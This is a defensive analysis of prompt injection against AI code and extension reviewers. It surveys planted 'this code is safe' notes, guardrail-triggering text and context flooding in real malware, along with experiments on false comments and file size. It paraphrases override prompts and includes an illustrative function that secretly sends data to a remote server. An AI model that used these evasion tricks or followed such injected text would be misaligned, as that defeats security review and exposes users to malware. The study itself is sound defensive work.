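# Prompt injection against AI code and extension reviewers, and the limits of AI self-review

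## How can code carry instructions to the model that reviews it?

Code review means having someone other than the author check software before other people rely on it. Programmers used to do this work, but software companies now give part of it to large language models, which are trained to continue text and are good at explaining what a program does. An AI reviewer is a language model, alone or with tools, that reads code and returns a judgement on it. Its final answer, such as malicious or benign, approve or reject, is the verdict. AI review already happens on a very large scale. GitHub, a site where programmers store and share code, tested two versions of its Copilot reviewer on 1.4 million proposed changes, according to Help Net Security's *GitHub Copilot brings multiple AI reviewers to the same code change* (2026).

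Usually, a colleague proposes a change and the model looks for mistakes, with no attacker involved. But when a stranger wrote the code, they also wrote the text that accompanies it, and some of that text may be intended for the model, which reads it along with the code. Security researchers use the term "prompt injection" for text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions instead of its user's.

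### One run of text

In a basic AI scanner, the developer writes some instructions (act as a malware analyst, say whether the following file is dangerous), and a program pastes the suspect file in after them. Cohen (2026) explains in *The malware that wants your AI scanner to look away* that the model then reads all of it as one run of text and has no dependable way to tell where the instructions stop and the file starts. Cohen works for JFrog, a company that studies attacks on software packages. Commercial reviewers use more sources. Copilot, for example, can also draw on guidance files stored with the project, "skills" (folders of instructions for particular tasks) and connected outside tools.

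A model reads its operator's instructions and the file under review as tokens, which are short fragments of text, and predicts the next token from all the tokens so far. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025 by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that this leaves no way to enforce a boundary between the instructions and the file. It points out that developers distinguish "data" from "instruction", while the model only predicts the next token. Developers can put markers around the file, or train the model to rank its operator's instructions above anything in the file that looks like an instruction. Both measures make an attack harder, but neither guarantees protection, because the model only learns a tendency to respect the boundary.

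Telephone networks once carried control signals on the same line as callers' voices, so a caller who whistled the right tone could operate the switch. Schneier on Security's *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024) recounts how AT&T ended this by moving the control signals to a separate channel. The essay describes prompt injection as the same kind of vulnerability, along with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a field meant for data such as a name.

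Cohen also calls prompt injection the same old mistake as SQL injection, a comparison David C thinks is dangerous. They agree that in both cases something meant as data ends up working as a command, but they disagree about whether prompt injection can be cured. A database engine treats commands and data differently, so programmers can send the two separately and the engine will never run the data. No one has an equivalent for language models, and David C thinks there may never be one. He prefers to think of the model as an inherently confusable "confused deputy", a trusted component that an outsider can talk into misusing its powers. His argument seems stronger, because the SQL analogy describes what goes wrong but also suggests that a fix is coming.

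### What the machine runs and what only readers see

Computers execute source code, but people also read it. Programmers therefore include material for readers that does nothing when the program runs, such as comments (notes in ordinary language), descriptive names and documentation. The following invented Python function shows how much this material can differ from what the computer executes.

```python
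# Tidies a note for printing. Works offline. The security team has checked it.
def tidy_note(note):
    send(REMOTE_SERVER, note)
    return note.strip()
```

Python's compiler, which turns this text into something a computer can run, discards the first line and keeps the names only as labels. Changing `tidy_note` to `steal_note` throughout the program would not affect what the computer does. It would still send a copy of the note to another machine and then trim the blank space from the note's ends.

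A person who reads as far as the third line sees that it conflicts with the comment, but someone in a hurry may not get that far. A careful reader also knows that anyone can write a comment, and can ask the security team whether it ever saw the function.

A model reads the comment, the names and the working code as a single sequence of tokens, and any of them can change its verdict. In an example this short, a current model would very probably notice the contradiction. In a ten-thousand-line program where an innocently named function in another file does the sending, the comment becomes the clearest available statement of what the code is for. Names can also mislead the model, and they are less conspicuous than comments. Cloudflare (2026), which runs other people's code on its network, advises operators of AI scanners to replace variable names with neutral ones before the review, because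 a friendly name might sway the model.

An attacker can also write instructions to the model outside the comments, for example in a message that the program prints on the screen. The message is part of the code that runs, but the computer only copies its characters, while the model reads them as language.

### Orders and false claims

Prompt injection is direct when the attacker types instructions to the model, as when someone tells a chatbot to disregard its rules. It is indirect when the instructions are inside material that somebody else asked the model to read. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's AI system to approve the candidate. *Not what you've signed up for* (2023) demonstrated indirect injection against several kinds of application built on language models. Almost everything an attacker can do to an AI code reviewer is indirect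 injection, since the attacker reaches the model through the code it reviews.

The comment in the invented function, however, is a false safety claim rather than an instruction. A false safety claim is text beside the code that wrongly says the code is safe or that someone has checked it. A model asked to judge the code can treat such a claim as evidence without following any instruction. Writers on the subject often don't distinguish false safety claims from instructions. Cloudflare, for example, uses "indirect prompt injection" for planted notices that consist almost entirely of reassurance.

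The distinction between orders and false claims affects what a defence can achieve. Even a model that never followed orders found in a file would have to decide how far to believe the comments. It could not sensibly ignore them all, because in honest code they are useful. GitHub encourages project owners to write a file for Copilot that explains, among other things, which patterns in the code are intentional. Such a note is meant to keep the reviewer from flagging something odd but harmless. An attacker's false claim has the same form and purpose, so the reviewer has to check it against what the code does, which is the hard part of code review anyway.

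### What an attacker might want from the reviewer

The obvious aim is to make the reviewer approve bad code. An attacker can try to do this by writing orders or false claims into the code, or by concealing what the code does without addressing the model at all.

An attacker may instead try to prevent any verdict. *Not what you've signed up for* already included attacks in 2023 that only spoiled a search tool's output. Against a code reviewer, an attacker can include text that triggers the guardrail, a safety layer that monitors a model's input and output and cuts off the reply when the subject looks forbidden. This can destroy an analysis that was going well, and Cohen reports that the makers of a real piece of malware tried it. A large amount of text can have a similar effect. When Cloudflare put a thousand or more reassuring comments into a script, some of the stronger models it tested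 returned garbled text or refusals where the scanner expected a one-word answer.

Whether a missing verdict helps the attacker depends on how the developer wrote the program around the model to respond when it gets no usable answer. If the program holds the file for a human, the attacker has gained little and has probably drawn attention. If it treats a missing answer as "nothing found", the file goes through.

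The attacker's remaining aim is to make the reviewer act, which is possible only when the reviewer is an agent, a model that can use tools, for instance to run commands or edit files. The verdict may then hardly matter to the attacker, who wants a password copied or a file altered during the review. David C's rule for designers is to assume the worst case, in which the attacker can use the tools directly. For agents that start work automatically, GitHub warns that input from untrusted users could become part of the agent's prompt, and it has the owner choose which tools the agent may use to limit the damage.

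How often injection succeeds varies a good deal between systems. Help Net Security's *Anthropic to put AI in charge of reviewing Claude Code actions* (2026) reports that in a test by the firm Trajectory Labs, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against Anthropic models running in "auto mode", where a second AI component checks each action before it happens. On the same benchmark, 5.83% of attempts succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with a comparable check switched on, and 19.03% succeeded when the agent had full access. These results are for agents in general and don't measure how well a model judges hostile code.

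### Where the reviews happen

In pull-request review, the model examines a proposed change to an existing project. The proposal, called a pull request, has a title and a description, and on many public projects a stranger can submit one. The model sees the change and often the surrounding code, and it usually posts its findings where the author can read them. This helps honest authors, but it also lets a dishonest one act as an adaptive attacker, who reads the findings and tries again.

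A pull request can also include edits to the instructions that Copilot will follow when reviewing it. Copilot used to take a project's custom review instructions from the base branch, the version of the project that the change would join. In July 2026, GitHub (2026) switched the source to the head branch, the version that contains the proposed change, so that teams could try out new instructions before adopting them. GitHub's *Copilot code review* (2026) lists the use of custom instructions among the settings that administrators can manage for each repository (a project's store of code).

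Stores and registries do a different kind of scanning, in which the platform's operator checks what outsiders upload before or while other people use it. The uploads may be browser add-ons, editor plugins or packages, which are bundles of ready-made code that programmers build into their own work. ("Extension" here means any third-party software added to a larger program.) Cloudflare does something similar with Workers, the small scripts that its customers run on its network. A platform at that scale can't have a person review every file, so a program has to be able to act on the scanner's output.

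In the third setting, a user asks a coding assistant whether an extension is safe before installing it. Cohen says development teams commonly run suspicious packages past a model before trusting them, and calls the habit sensible. This reviewer may have the fewest checks around it. It often runs on the user's own computer with some of the user's permissions, and there may be no second reviewer.

### How much an AI approval can decide

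Many repositories require one or more approvals before anyone can merge a change, that is, add it to the main version. By default, Copilot only leaves comments. GitHub's *Copilot code review can now approve pull requests* (2026), published on 1 September, describes an option for administrators to let Copilot submit approvals that count towards the requirement. The option is in public preview. Administrators can limit it to certain files, and new changes to the pull request cancel an approval already given. Every Copilot review also includes an "approval assessment", an opinion on whether the change is ready, but this alone does not count towards the requirement.

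Anthropic went further in November 2026 with a set of agents that review pull requests, repair them and approve those that a team's written policy allows. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Ship* (2026) warns that the system may miss security vulnerabilities. Anthropic's *Claude Approvals* explains that if a GitHub rule requires one approval, Claude's can satisfy it. A policy can let a change written by a bot merge without a person looking at it. A badly written policy can have Claude approve a change that nothing has reviewed, because permission to approve does not by itself start a review. Claude Approvals reads its policy from the project's default branch, so a pull request can't rewrite the rules for its own approval. Anthropic recommends that most customers start in a mode that only reports what the policy would have decided.

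In August 2026, auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on several subscription plans, so an AI component now judges commands that users would otherwise have had to approve on their own machines. The case for the change is that people were poor at spotting danger. Help Net Security reports that in Anthropic's own study of 1,053 paid testers, the humans blocked 13.6% of dangerous commands and auto mode blocked 89%.

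That is a fair argument for replacing a tired person who clicks "yes", but it doesn't show that AI approval is safe against a hostile author. The published figures for code review mostly measure how well a reviewer catches mistakes in everyday development, where the author usually wants them found. For example, GitHub estimates that its three levels of Copilot review caught between 57% and 67% of the issues in its tests, as Help Net Security reports. Anthropic similarly says that its Claude Code team more than doubled its merged pull requests between June and September, while the share it later had to undo fell by over 40%.

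## What have attackers planted in real packages and scripts?

Since June 2025, security companies have found text aimed at AI reviewers in malware, public software packages and scripts on Cloudflare's network. Fetterman (2026) calls these tricks "AI-analysis evasion" in *Ignore all instructions and read this blog*. The first attackers asked the reviewer to report the code as safe. By mid-2026, several were trying to make the reviewer stop before it reached a verdict.

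### Text that vouches for the code

In early June 2025, an anonymous user in the Netherlands uploaded a Windows program to VirusTotal, a website that runs files through many malware scanners. *In the Wild* (2025), by the security company Check Point, describes the program, which its author had named Skynet. It checked whether it was running on the kind of simulated computer that analysts use, tried to read the key that lets the user log in to other machines, and set up a connection through the anonymity network Tor. It looked half-finished, because it printed the collected data to the screen without sending it to anyone.

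One malware author included a paragraph in the code asking any AI model to drop its earlier instructions, act as a calculator, and acknowledge its new role by replying that it had found no malware. Check Point's researchers gave the code to two OpenAI models, o3 and GPT-4.1, and both carried on with the analysis. The researchers thought the prompt was badly written and could only guess why it was there. They still expected more attempts, because malware authors had found hundreds of ways to evade an earlier defence, the sandbox (an isolated machine for running suspect files).

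In late 2025, the security firm Koi reported on eslint-plugin-unicorn-ts-2, a malicious package that people were installing from npm, the main public registry for JavaScript packages. The attacker had copied the documentation of a popular add-on for ESLint, a tool that checks code for mistakes, and presented the package as a version of that add-on, but it did nothing useful. On installation, it ran a script that collected the computer's environment variables, which often include passwords and access keys, and sent them to the attacker through a legitimate automation service.

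The attacker had also stored a sentence in a variable that no other part of the program used. In that sentence, the attacker told the reader to forget everything it knew and falsely claimed that the code was legitimate and had passed internal tests. Koi's AI engine, which had been trained to look for such text, flagged the package because of this sentence. Koi doesn't know whether the sentence ever fooled another tool.

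Koi's timeline suggests that the package stayed on npm for reasons unrelated to the planted sentence. An automated Open Source Security Foundation project identified version 1.1.6 as malicious on 20 February 2024, the month the attacker uploaded the package. npm didn't remove the package, and the databases that recorded the finding listed only that version, so the attacker could publish new versions that carried no warning. Anyone could still install the package in December 2025, when The Hacker News counted 18,988 downloads. Koi found the planted sentence in one of the later versions, 1.2.1, so the upload date doesn't show that anyone was writing for AI scanners in early 2024, and the download count covers versions that may not have contained the sentence.

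In March 2026, Cloudflare's threat researchers were investigating a surge in customers' scripts for running VPNs and proxies, which relay other people's internet traffic, on its Workers platform. One script contained thousands of lines of repetitive notices addressed to AI code reviewers. The author described the script as a legitimate private project that collected no data without permission and hid nothing, then repeated similar assurances in Spanish, Croatian, Estonian, Lithuanian and Latvian. The author also listed changing the contents of a web page as a routine task, which is a job for code in a browser and an odd description of a proxy, so the text may have been generic and pasted in.

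Cloudflare's team found the notices during routine analysis and reports no case in which one got a script past its scanner. The team then tested similar comments on seven models to measure how often they changed the verdict.

### Text that stops the analysis

The most elaborate examples come from Shai-Hulud, a family of worms (malware that spreads by copying itself) that infects software packages. They steal credentials from programmers' computers and from the servers that build their software, then use them to publish infected versions of packages the victims maintain. In a wave called Miasma, the attackers hijacked 96 package versions belonging to Red Hat's cloud services, according to JFrog (2026). Programmers who checked the publisher's name would have seen Red Hat, a company they had good reason to trust.

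Cohen examined one sample from the npm campaign in June 2026. The malicious code was a large scrambled block that ran when someone installed the package. The attackers had put English text above it that resembled classified documents about weapons. They wanted only to trigger the model's guardrail so that the scanner would return a refusal, and they did not claim that the file was safe.

Cohen gave the file to several models through chatbots, an API, a coding agent and a local machine. Claude's guardrail blocked the analysis in every setup. Gemini's chatbot identified the malware, but a guardrail blocked the response when Cohen used the API. ChatGPT, DeepSeek and a local copy of Qwen read the whole file and pointed out both the scrambled code and the planted text. In the blocked cases, part of the answer sometimes appeared before the guardrail erased it, and the model was already noting the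 suspicious code.

This is the best evidence that text from a real attack can disrupt current models. Cohen attributes the refusals to the planted text, but he reports no run without it. He says guardrails also react to malware, so the code below the text may have contributed. He also warns that the results depend on how each company had configured its products at the time.

From 6 June, the attackers spread a related variant called Hades through PyPI, the public registry for Python packages. Socket's *Mini Shai-Hulud, Miasma, and Hades Worms Target Bioinformatics and MCP Developers* describes a large comment at the start of the malicious JavaScript file that contains fake system instructions and forbidden subject matter. Socket, which sells package-scanning tools, thinks the attackers wrote the comment to disrupt AI scanners and analysts' AI assistants.

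JFrog disagrees with Socket about the purpose of the planted prompts. It found them in four Hades packages, all of which are also on Socket's list, and interprets them as jailbreaks, prompts meant to make a model ignore its safety rules. On this reading, the target is the victim's own coding assistant, which may load files from an infected project automatically. The rest of the malware gives this reading some support, because it writes its own entries into the settings of Claude, Codex, Copilot and other assistants. But SC Media reports that the text contains instructions to help produce biological and nuclear weapons. Those instructions would probably make an assistant refuse, which wouldn't help an attacker trying to take it over, so Socket's explanation seems better for this text.

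Socket's report also includes an AI analysis that correctly describes one of the Hades packages, langchain-core-mcp. But this package came without the JavaScript file that contains the planted comment, so we can't tell from this result whether Socket's scanner withstands the trick.

The same campaign also tried the older approach. StepSecurity, another company that investigated it, found a prompt telling the model to ignore the malicious code and report the package as clean, according to ITmedia's *マルウェアに「核兵器の作り方を教えて」 AIによるコード解析を止めさせる新手口「GuardBreaker」*. Later in June, SentinelLabs reported a Mac backdoor, linked to North Korea, that used prompt injection against AI tools for sorting suspicious files (Mascellino, 2026, *macOS Backdoor Uses Prompt Injection to Evade AI Triage*).

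An attacker can also stop an analysis by filling the model's context window, the limited amount of text it can take in at once, so that the code doesn't fit. Socket found an npm package that combined prompt injection and guardrail-triggering comments with a flood of text meant to fill this window. ITmedia describes what is probably the same package, where the attacker repeated one short phrase tens of thousands of times before the malicious script. Neither account identifies a scanner that missed the package as a result.

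In September 2026, the security company ESET gave the refusal trick its own name in *GuardBreaker* (2026). UAC-0099, a group with links to Russia, had used the trick against a target in Ukraine. The group's script downloaded a second program that would fetch more malware, and a comment in the script asked for help making a nuclear weapon. According to ITmedia, ESET considers this a very simple form of prompt injection. ESET takes the comment as a sign that the group expected the target's defences to include AI, much as the group had checked for conventional analysis tools in another recent attack. The comment doesn't show whether the target had an AI scanner or what such a scanner did.

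### When no verdict counts as no problem

A refusal or a garbled answer helps the attacker only if the program around the model then lets the file through. Suppose the model must answer "malicious" or "benign". The program could block a file only when the answer is "malicious", or release a file only when the answer is "benign". Both rules give the same result when the model answers as asked, but if it refuses or garbles its answer, the first rule lets the file through and the second blocks it.

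| Model's reply | Block only if "malicious" | Release only if "benign" |
|---|---|---|
| "malicious" | blocked | blocked |
| "benign" | released | released |
| refusal, garbled text or no reply | released | blocked |

The first rule fails open, meaning a file goes through if the check breaks down. The second fails closed and blocks the file until some check returns a usable answer. Under the first rule, an attacker only has to stop the model from producing one particular word, and doesn't need to persuade it of anything. Cloudflare calls this a significant remaining risk for scanners that depend on an answer in a fixed format.

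Cohen advises treating a refusal as a null result and passing the file to another kind of check, such as rule-based analysis, a sandbox or a person. His Shai-Hulud sample shows why this can work. The package was supposed to contain only type definitions, which describe data and have no reason to run anything during installation, yet it ran a program when someone installed it. A simple rule can catch that without reading the planted text. ITmedia reports that ESET similarly recommends further checks when output is missing.

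Failing closed will delay some honest developers, because some harmless files will also trigger a guardrail. A security tool might include samples of attack text, for instance. ESET warns that an attacker might steer an AI agent into actions that need human review and exploit the delay. Holding a file therefore protects people only if they can't install it while it waits.

It also doesn't catch a well-formed answer based on only part of the file. If enough added text pushes the malicious code out of the context window, the model may return "benign" for the part it received, and the program will release the file under either rule. The program therefore has to check that the model received the whole file. Even that may not be enough, since a model can miss malicious code among thousands of other lines.

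People who ask a coding assistant about an extension have to apply the rule themselves. If the assistant declines to answer, or comments on the documentation but not the code, the extension is still unreviewed.

### Attempts and successes

None of these reports documents a scanner in everyday use that passed malicious code because of the planted text. The sample Check Point found failed against both models Check Point tried, Koi doesn't know what happened elsewhere, and Cohen's refusals come from his own tests. The finds show that attackers are trying, but reveal much less about how often it works. Their persistence is only weak evidence that it does, because adding a comment takes almost no effort.

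A successful injection would also be hard to detect. Koi and Cloudflare found their examples because their systems or staff flagged something in the text. If the text had worked, the scanner would have passed the file, and probably no one would have reported it. Investigators may still discover the malware later, perhaps after a victim complains, and then read the text. But they would need the scanner's records to learn whether it had passed the file, and they would have to compare scans with and without the text to learn why.

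The known examples are probably cruder than average for the same reason. Thousands of lines addressed to AI reviewers are easy to spot, but a single comment falsely saying that a function works offline looks like ordinary documentation. An investigator who found that comment in malware might not count it as an attack on an AI reviewer.

There is also a bias in the other direction, because most of these reports come from companies that sell security products and have a reason to present a new kind of attack as important. Koi, for example, ends its account with an invitation to book a demonstration. However, Check Point and Koi both say plainly that they have no evidence of such an attack working.

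Larger counts exist for a related problem, components that try to control an agent while it works. OX Security examined 542,207 open-source components between July and October 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path*. The company found prompt injection or tool poisoning (planting instructions in the description of a tool that an agent uses) in 26% of the agent skills it had flagged as suspicious. It found the same in 22% of flagged MCP servers, programs that connect agents to outside tools and data. Because these percentages cover only flagged components, and most of those were meant to control a working agent, we can't use them to estimate how many packages contain text written for a reviewer.

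## Do false safety comments change a reviewer's verdict?

Two large experiments in early 2026 tested whether false safety comments change a model's verdict by giving models the same code with and without the comments. In both, the experimenters wrote the comments in advance and didn't adapt them to a model's answers, unlike the attacker in *ALIBI* (2026), who keeps refining a comment in response to the reviewer's answers.

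### Short programs with one fault each

Thornton (2026), in *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think*, tested eight models on 100 short programs, each with one vulnerability (a mistake that an attacker could exploit). Thornton wrote the programs for the test, 50 in Python, 30 in JavaScript and 20 in Java. Each had several versions that ran identically and differed only in their comments. In the version most relevant here, the comments falsely claimed, for example, that the code had already passed a security review or that another system was filtering out dangerous input. The example that Thornton prints also tells the reviewer not to report the vulnerability, so the test mixes instructions with false safety claims.

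The study contains 9,366 evaluations, but its main result comes from 773 pairs. In each pair, a model reviewed the same program first with no comments and then with false safety comments.

| Model | Faults found, no comments | Faults found, false comments | Newly missed | Newly found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 95.0% | 94.0% | 1 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 93.0% | 91.9% | 3 | 2 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 91.9% | 91.9% | 4 | 4 |
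| DeepSeek Chat | 89.0% | 93.0% | 1 | 5 |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 96.1% | 92.0% | 5 | 2 |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 72.0% | 71.0% | 12 | 11 |
| Qwen 2.5 72B | 70.0% | 72.0% | 10 | 12 |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B | 53.0% | 58.0% | 12 | 17 |

Thornton reports these results as changes of −5% to +4% in the miss rate. With the false comments present, one model found five more faults per hundred, another found about four fewer, and the rest fell in between.

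Similar totals can hide changes in individual verdicts. Gemini found 91.9% of the faults both times, but the second time it missed four that it had found before and found four that it had missed. Thornton therefore used McNemar's test, which looks only at the verdicts that changed. If the comments had no overall effect, a changed verdict would be equally likely to go in either direction.

DeepSeek Chat changed its verdict on six programs, one for the worse and five for the better. Six coin tosses can come out in 64 ways. One of these has no heads and six have exactly one, and the same goes for tails, so the chance of a split at least this uneven is:

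2 × (1 + 6) / 64 ≈ 0.219

Researchers usually call an effect statistically significant only if its p-value is below 0.05. The lowest of the eight p-values came from a model that did better with the false comments. The table's last two columns total 48 new misses and 53 new finds.

The test could still have missed a small effect. If a model had missed five more programs and newly found none, the p-value would have been 0.0625, which is still not significant. Thornton also ran each combination only once, and models can answer the same question differently each time. Some of the 101 changed verdicts probably had nothing to do with the comments, while others may have been real successes for the attacker, offset by faults the models newly found in other programs. One such success may be a Java program whose authorization fault three of the five commercial models missed when the false comments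 were present. An attacker needs only one program like that, but would find it hard to know which one when writing the comments in advance.

More elaborate comments didn't work any better. Thornton tried invented records of formal security reviews, long and accurate comments on the harmless parts of the code, and false arguments that cited real security standards. When Thornton compared the same 30 programs with and without these comments, the effect on detection was close to zero. The raw results showed a rise of 2 to 11 points, but Thornton had added the comments only to the first 30 programs, which were easier. Without comments, the commercial models found 98.0% of the faults in those 30 programs and 90.5% in the other 70.

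The scoring may have understated the effect of false comments. Thornton's software counted a fault as found if the model's reply contained any of several keywords for that fault, so a model that repeated a comment's assurance that there was no SQL injection could get credit for finding one. Such echoes would make the false comments look less effective than they were, because a model can't echo a comment that isn't there. Thornton argues that the errors cancel out because the same keywords apply to both versions. Thornton checked 14 replies to the elaborate comments and found one echo, but 14 replies are too few to rule out an error of several points, which is as large as any of the changes in the table.

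### Faults that the models missed anyway

The programs were typically 15 to 60 lines long, and Thornton had confirmed that static-analysis tools, which check code against rules without running it, could detect every fault. A model can often find the fault in code this short, so it has less need to rely on comments.

Comments can matter much more in harder code. *LLMs as Validators for Cross-Chain Bridges* (2026) tested whether models could identify a missing safety check in programs that connect one blockchain to another. When the researchers left the original comments in, correct diagnoses rose from 24% to 60%, mostly in cases where a comment revealed what was missing. The model that did best without comments also improved, from 218 to 306 correct diagnoses in 400 runs. These comments were helpful, so the experiment doesn't measure how much damage false comments would have done. But it suggests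 that models use comments, and that Thornton's result doesn't come from models ignoring them.

In Thornton's test, the choice of model made a much bigger difference than the comments did. Without any comments, the five commercial models found 89% to 96% of the faults, and the three models that anyone can download found 53% to 72%.

Most of the commercial models missed certain faults even in uncommented code. Four of the five missed a login check that leaked secrets through its timing. For example, if a program compares a password one character at a time and stops at the first mismatch, it takes slightly longer when more of the guess is right. An attacker who measures the delay can work out the password. The comparison gives the correct answer, so a reviewer who checks only the code's results will miss the flaw.

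Three of the five missed a race condition, in which an attacker can change something after a program checks that it is safe but before the program uses it. Three also missed a Java program whose access rules were each correct on their own but unsafe together, and two missed a misuse of Java's cryptography functions.

Thornton concludes that these faults are a bigger problem for AI review than false comments are. That seems right for honest mistakes. A hostile author can also deliberately plant a fault that models usually miss, and doesn't need a false comment to hide it.

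### Malicious scripts with up to a thousand comments

Cloudflare used real scripts instead of invented programs like Thornton's. After finding the script with thousands of lines of notices to AI reviewers, its researchers took 100 other scripts from its Workers platform, all confirmed as malicious or abusive through its blocking rules. About half were for phishing, a third were proxies, and others involved file hosting and streaming abuse.

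Cloudflare tested three "frontier" models, meaning a company's most capable ones, and four "non-frontier" models, which are faster and cheaper. It doesn't name them. In a first round of 2,700 calls, the researchers used extracts of about 1,500 words and put the reassuring notice in one block. This made most of the cheaper models more likely to flag the code. In the second round, the researchers gave each model as much of the full script as it could take in, and inserted between one and 1,000 comments at random points between statements.

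| Model | Flagged, no comments | Flagged, 20 comments | Flagged, 1,000 comments |
|---|---|---|---|
| Frontier 1 | 67% | 67% | 76% |
| Frontier 2 | 61% | 64% | 68% |
| Frontier 3 | 62% | 67% | 75% |
| Non-frontier 1 | 90% | 67% | 72% |
| Non-frontier 2 | 65% | 75% | 91% |
| Non-frontier 3 | 72% | 67% | 68% |
| Non-frontier 4 | 59% | 65% | 72% |

Non-frontier model 1 fell from 90% to 67% with 20 comments, a far larger drop than any in Thornton's results. An attacker who knew that a platform relied on this model would have good reason to add comments. Only one other model did worse with 20 comments, by five points, and four did better. The average for all seven changed little, from 68.0% to 67.4%.

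With 1,000 comments, the average rose to 74.6%, and five of the seven models flagged more scripts than they had with none. Cloudflare attributes this to the repetition itself becoming a sign of fraud. This is plausible, since an honest programmer has no reason to tell an AI reviewer 1,000 times that a script is harmless.

The figures for 1,000 comments may be misleading, however, because frontier models 1 and 3 gave some unusable answers in those tests. Cloudflare doesn't publish how many. It excluded unusable answers from one of its other tables but doesn't say how it treated them in this one. If 20 of 100 answers from frontier model 1 were unusable, and its 76% covers only the other 80, the model flagged 61 scripts, fewer than it did without comments. A scanner that lets scripts through when it gets an unusable answer would then have become less safe.

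Cloudflare also translated the comments into Estonian, Chinese, Russian and Arabic. The language made the most difference to non-frontier model 3, which flagged 68% of the scripts when they contained 1,000 English comments and 82% when the comments were in Russian. Its output described the Russian comments as indicators of social engineering. Frontier model 1 flagged 76% with English comments and 83% with each of the other languages, while non-frontier model 2 flagged scripts most often when the comments were in English.

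Cloudflare says that frontier models 2 and 3 were biased against Chinese and Arabic, but its table for 1,000 comments doesn't support this for model 2, which flagged 68% with English comments, 69% with Chinese and 67% with Arabic. Averaged over all seven models, the flag rates run from 73% for Estonian to 78% for Russian, with English at 75%. An attacker would gain little by switching languages unless they knew which model they faced. The higher rate for Russian might be unfair to honest programmers who write in it, but Cloudflare tested no harmless scripts, so its results can't show whether it is.

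That omission affects all of these detection rates, and Thornton's study has the same gap. A model that called every script malicious would have scored 100% in Cloudflare's test, so we can't tell whether a high-scoring model recognizes malicious code well or just flags code too readily.

Cloudflare's totals also don't match its published list of seven models. It reports 18,400 calls, but seven models reading 23 versions of 100 scripts would make 16,100. It reports 789 usable answers for the scripts without comments, but seven models could have given at most 700. Both totals are consistent with eight models. Cloudflare may have left one model off the list or run one twice, so its pooled figures may not exactly match the table above.

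### Large files

Script size affected detection far more than the comments did. Cloudflare sorted the scripts into five groups and pooled the results from all the models.

| Script size | Scripts | Flagged, no comments | Flagged, 1 comment | Flagged, 20 comments |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Under 100KB | 36 | 94.1% | 93.7% | 99.0% |
| 100KB–500KB | 18 | 100.0% | 100.0% | 100.0% |
| 500KB–1MB | 3 | 70.8% | 65.2% | 63.6% |
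| 1MB–3MB | 10 | 70.0% | 69.6% | 72.5% |
| Over 3MB | 33 | 17.6% | 13.6% | 12.3% |

Models caught nearly all the malicious scripts under 500KB and missed more than four out of five of those over 3MB. Scripts get this large mostly because programmers bundle their code with ready-made libraries in a single file. This is normal practice, so a large file isn't suspicious in itself, and the malicious part may be a few lines among many thousands of harmless ones.

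A model can miss those lines because they lie outside its context window, or because it receives them but fails to notice them among everything else. Cloudflare blames both, but its results for the largest scripts can't separate the two causes, because its models' context windows held between 376KB and 2.8MB. No model saw all of any script over 3MB.

This also casts some doubt on the 90% score of non-frontier model 1, which had the smallest context window. Only 67 of the 100 scripts were under 3MB, so to reach 90% the model must have flagged at least 23 of the 33 largest, although it could read no more than about an eighth of each. That part may have been enough to identify them as malicious, but the model may also have been guessing "malicious" when it was unsure. If so, the comments may have done little more than change its guesses about code it couldn't see. Cloudflare would have to publish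 each model's results by file size to settle this.

Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *MalTotal*, did separate the two kinds of failure in a small trial with DeepSeek-V3. They gave the model 50 malicious JavaScript projects in three forms. Seven of the complete projects were too large for the context window, and the model missed seven of the other 43. When the researchers included only the files that called sensitive functions, two projects were still too large, and the model missed seven of the other 48. When they cut each project by hand to just the malicious code, the model missed one of the 50.

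So irrelevant code can hide malicious code even when the model can analyse the whole project. This didn't happen in Python, where the model missed none of the projects that fitted, although 20 of the 50 were too large to analyse whole. The third form was also an ideal case, since someone had to find the malicious code before cutting away the rest.

Research on older models supports this. Sovrano, Bauer and Bacchelli (2025), in *Large Language Models for In-File Vulnerability Localization*, moved the same vulnerable lines to different places in files of different sizes. The models, which included GPT-4o, were less likely to find a vulnerability near the end of a large file, even though the files were under 30,000 characters. Ryan, Khalil and colleagues (2026), in *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages*, asked 13 models to identify exactly what was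 malicious in each package. The models did worse on longer packages, and those with larger context windows did no better. Half of the malicious packages had 36 lines of code or fewer, so length can reduce performance long before the context window is full.

*CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) provides the best evidence from current package scanning. Three of its four authors work only for Socket, and the fourth works for both Socket and a university. They ran two kinds of scanner, each with three models, on 4,884 files from npm packages. Half of the files were malicious. The scanners missed 7% to 12% of all the malicious files. Among the 512 files longer than 25,000 tokens (roughly 100KB of ordinary code), they missed 28% to 40% of the malicious ones. Five of the six scanner-model combinations couldn't scan about 30% of these large files. The researchers counted unscanned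 files as benign because people couldn't check them all in a registry as large as npm.

Attackers can also inflate a file on purpose. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues ran a one-line program through an ordinary obfuscation tool, which rewrites code to make it hard to read, and the program grew from 6 tokens to 790. In June 2026, attackers in the Miasma campaign hid their code in ai-sdk-ollama, a package with over 100,000 weekly downloads. They stored it as a list of more than 1.3 million numbers that the program turned back into code when it ran. The file was 4.5MB, too large for many models, so it would have been a problem for a scanner whether or not it contained text addressed to the reviewer.

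### Do a few comments work better than many?

Cloudflare claims that false comments work best when they make up less than 1% of a file. Models flagged 53.3% of scripts in this range, which Cloudflare calls the "bypass zone", compared with 67.3% of scripts without comments. Techzine reported that detection "nearly halves" there, but the drop is about a fifth. The comparison has the same flaw as Thornton's first look at his elaborate comments, because the two groups don't contain the same mix of code. The claim could still be true, since a subtle lie is often more convincing than a repeated one.

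If 20 comments take up 4KB, they make up 29% of the file when added to a 10KB script, but only 0.1% when added to a 4MB script. The group where comments make up less than 1% of the file will therefore contain a large share of very big scripts, most of which models miss anyway.

A fairer test is to compare results for the same 100 scripts with and without comments. Cloudflare's size table makes this possible. Our calculation below, which is not Cloudflare's, multiplies the detection rate for each size group by the number of scripts in that group, then divides the total by 100.

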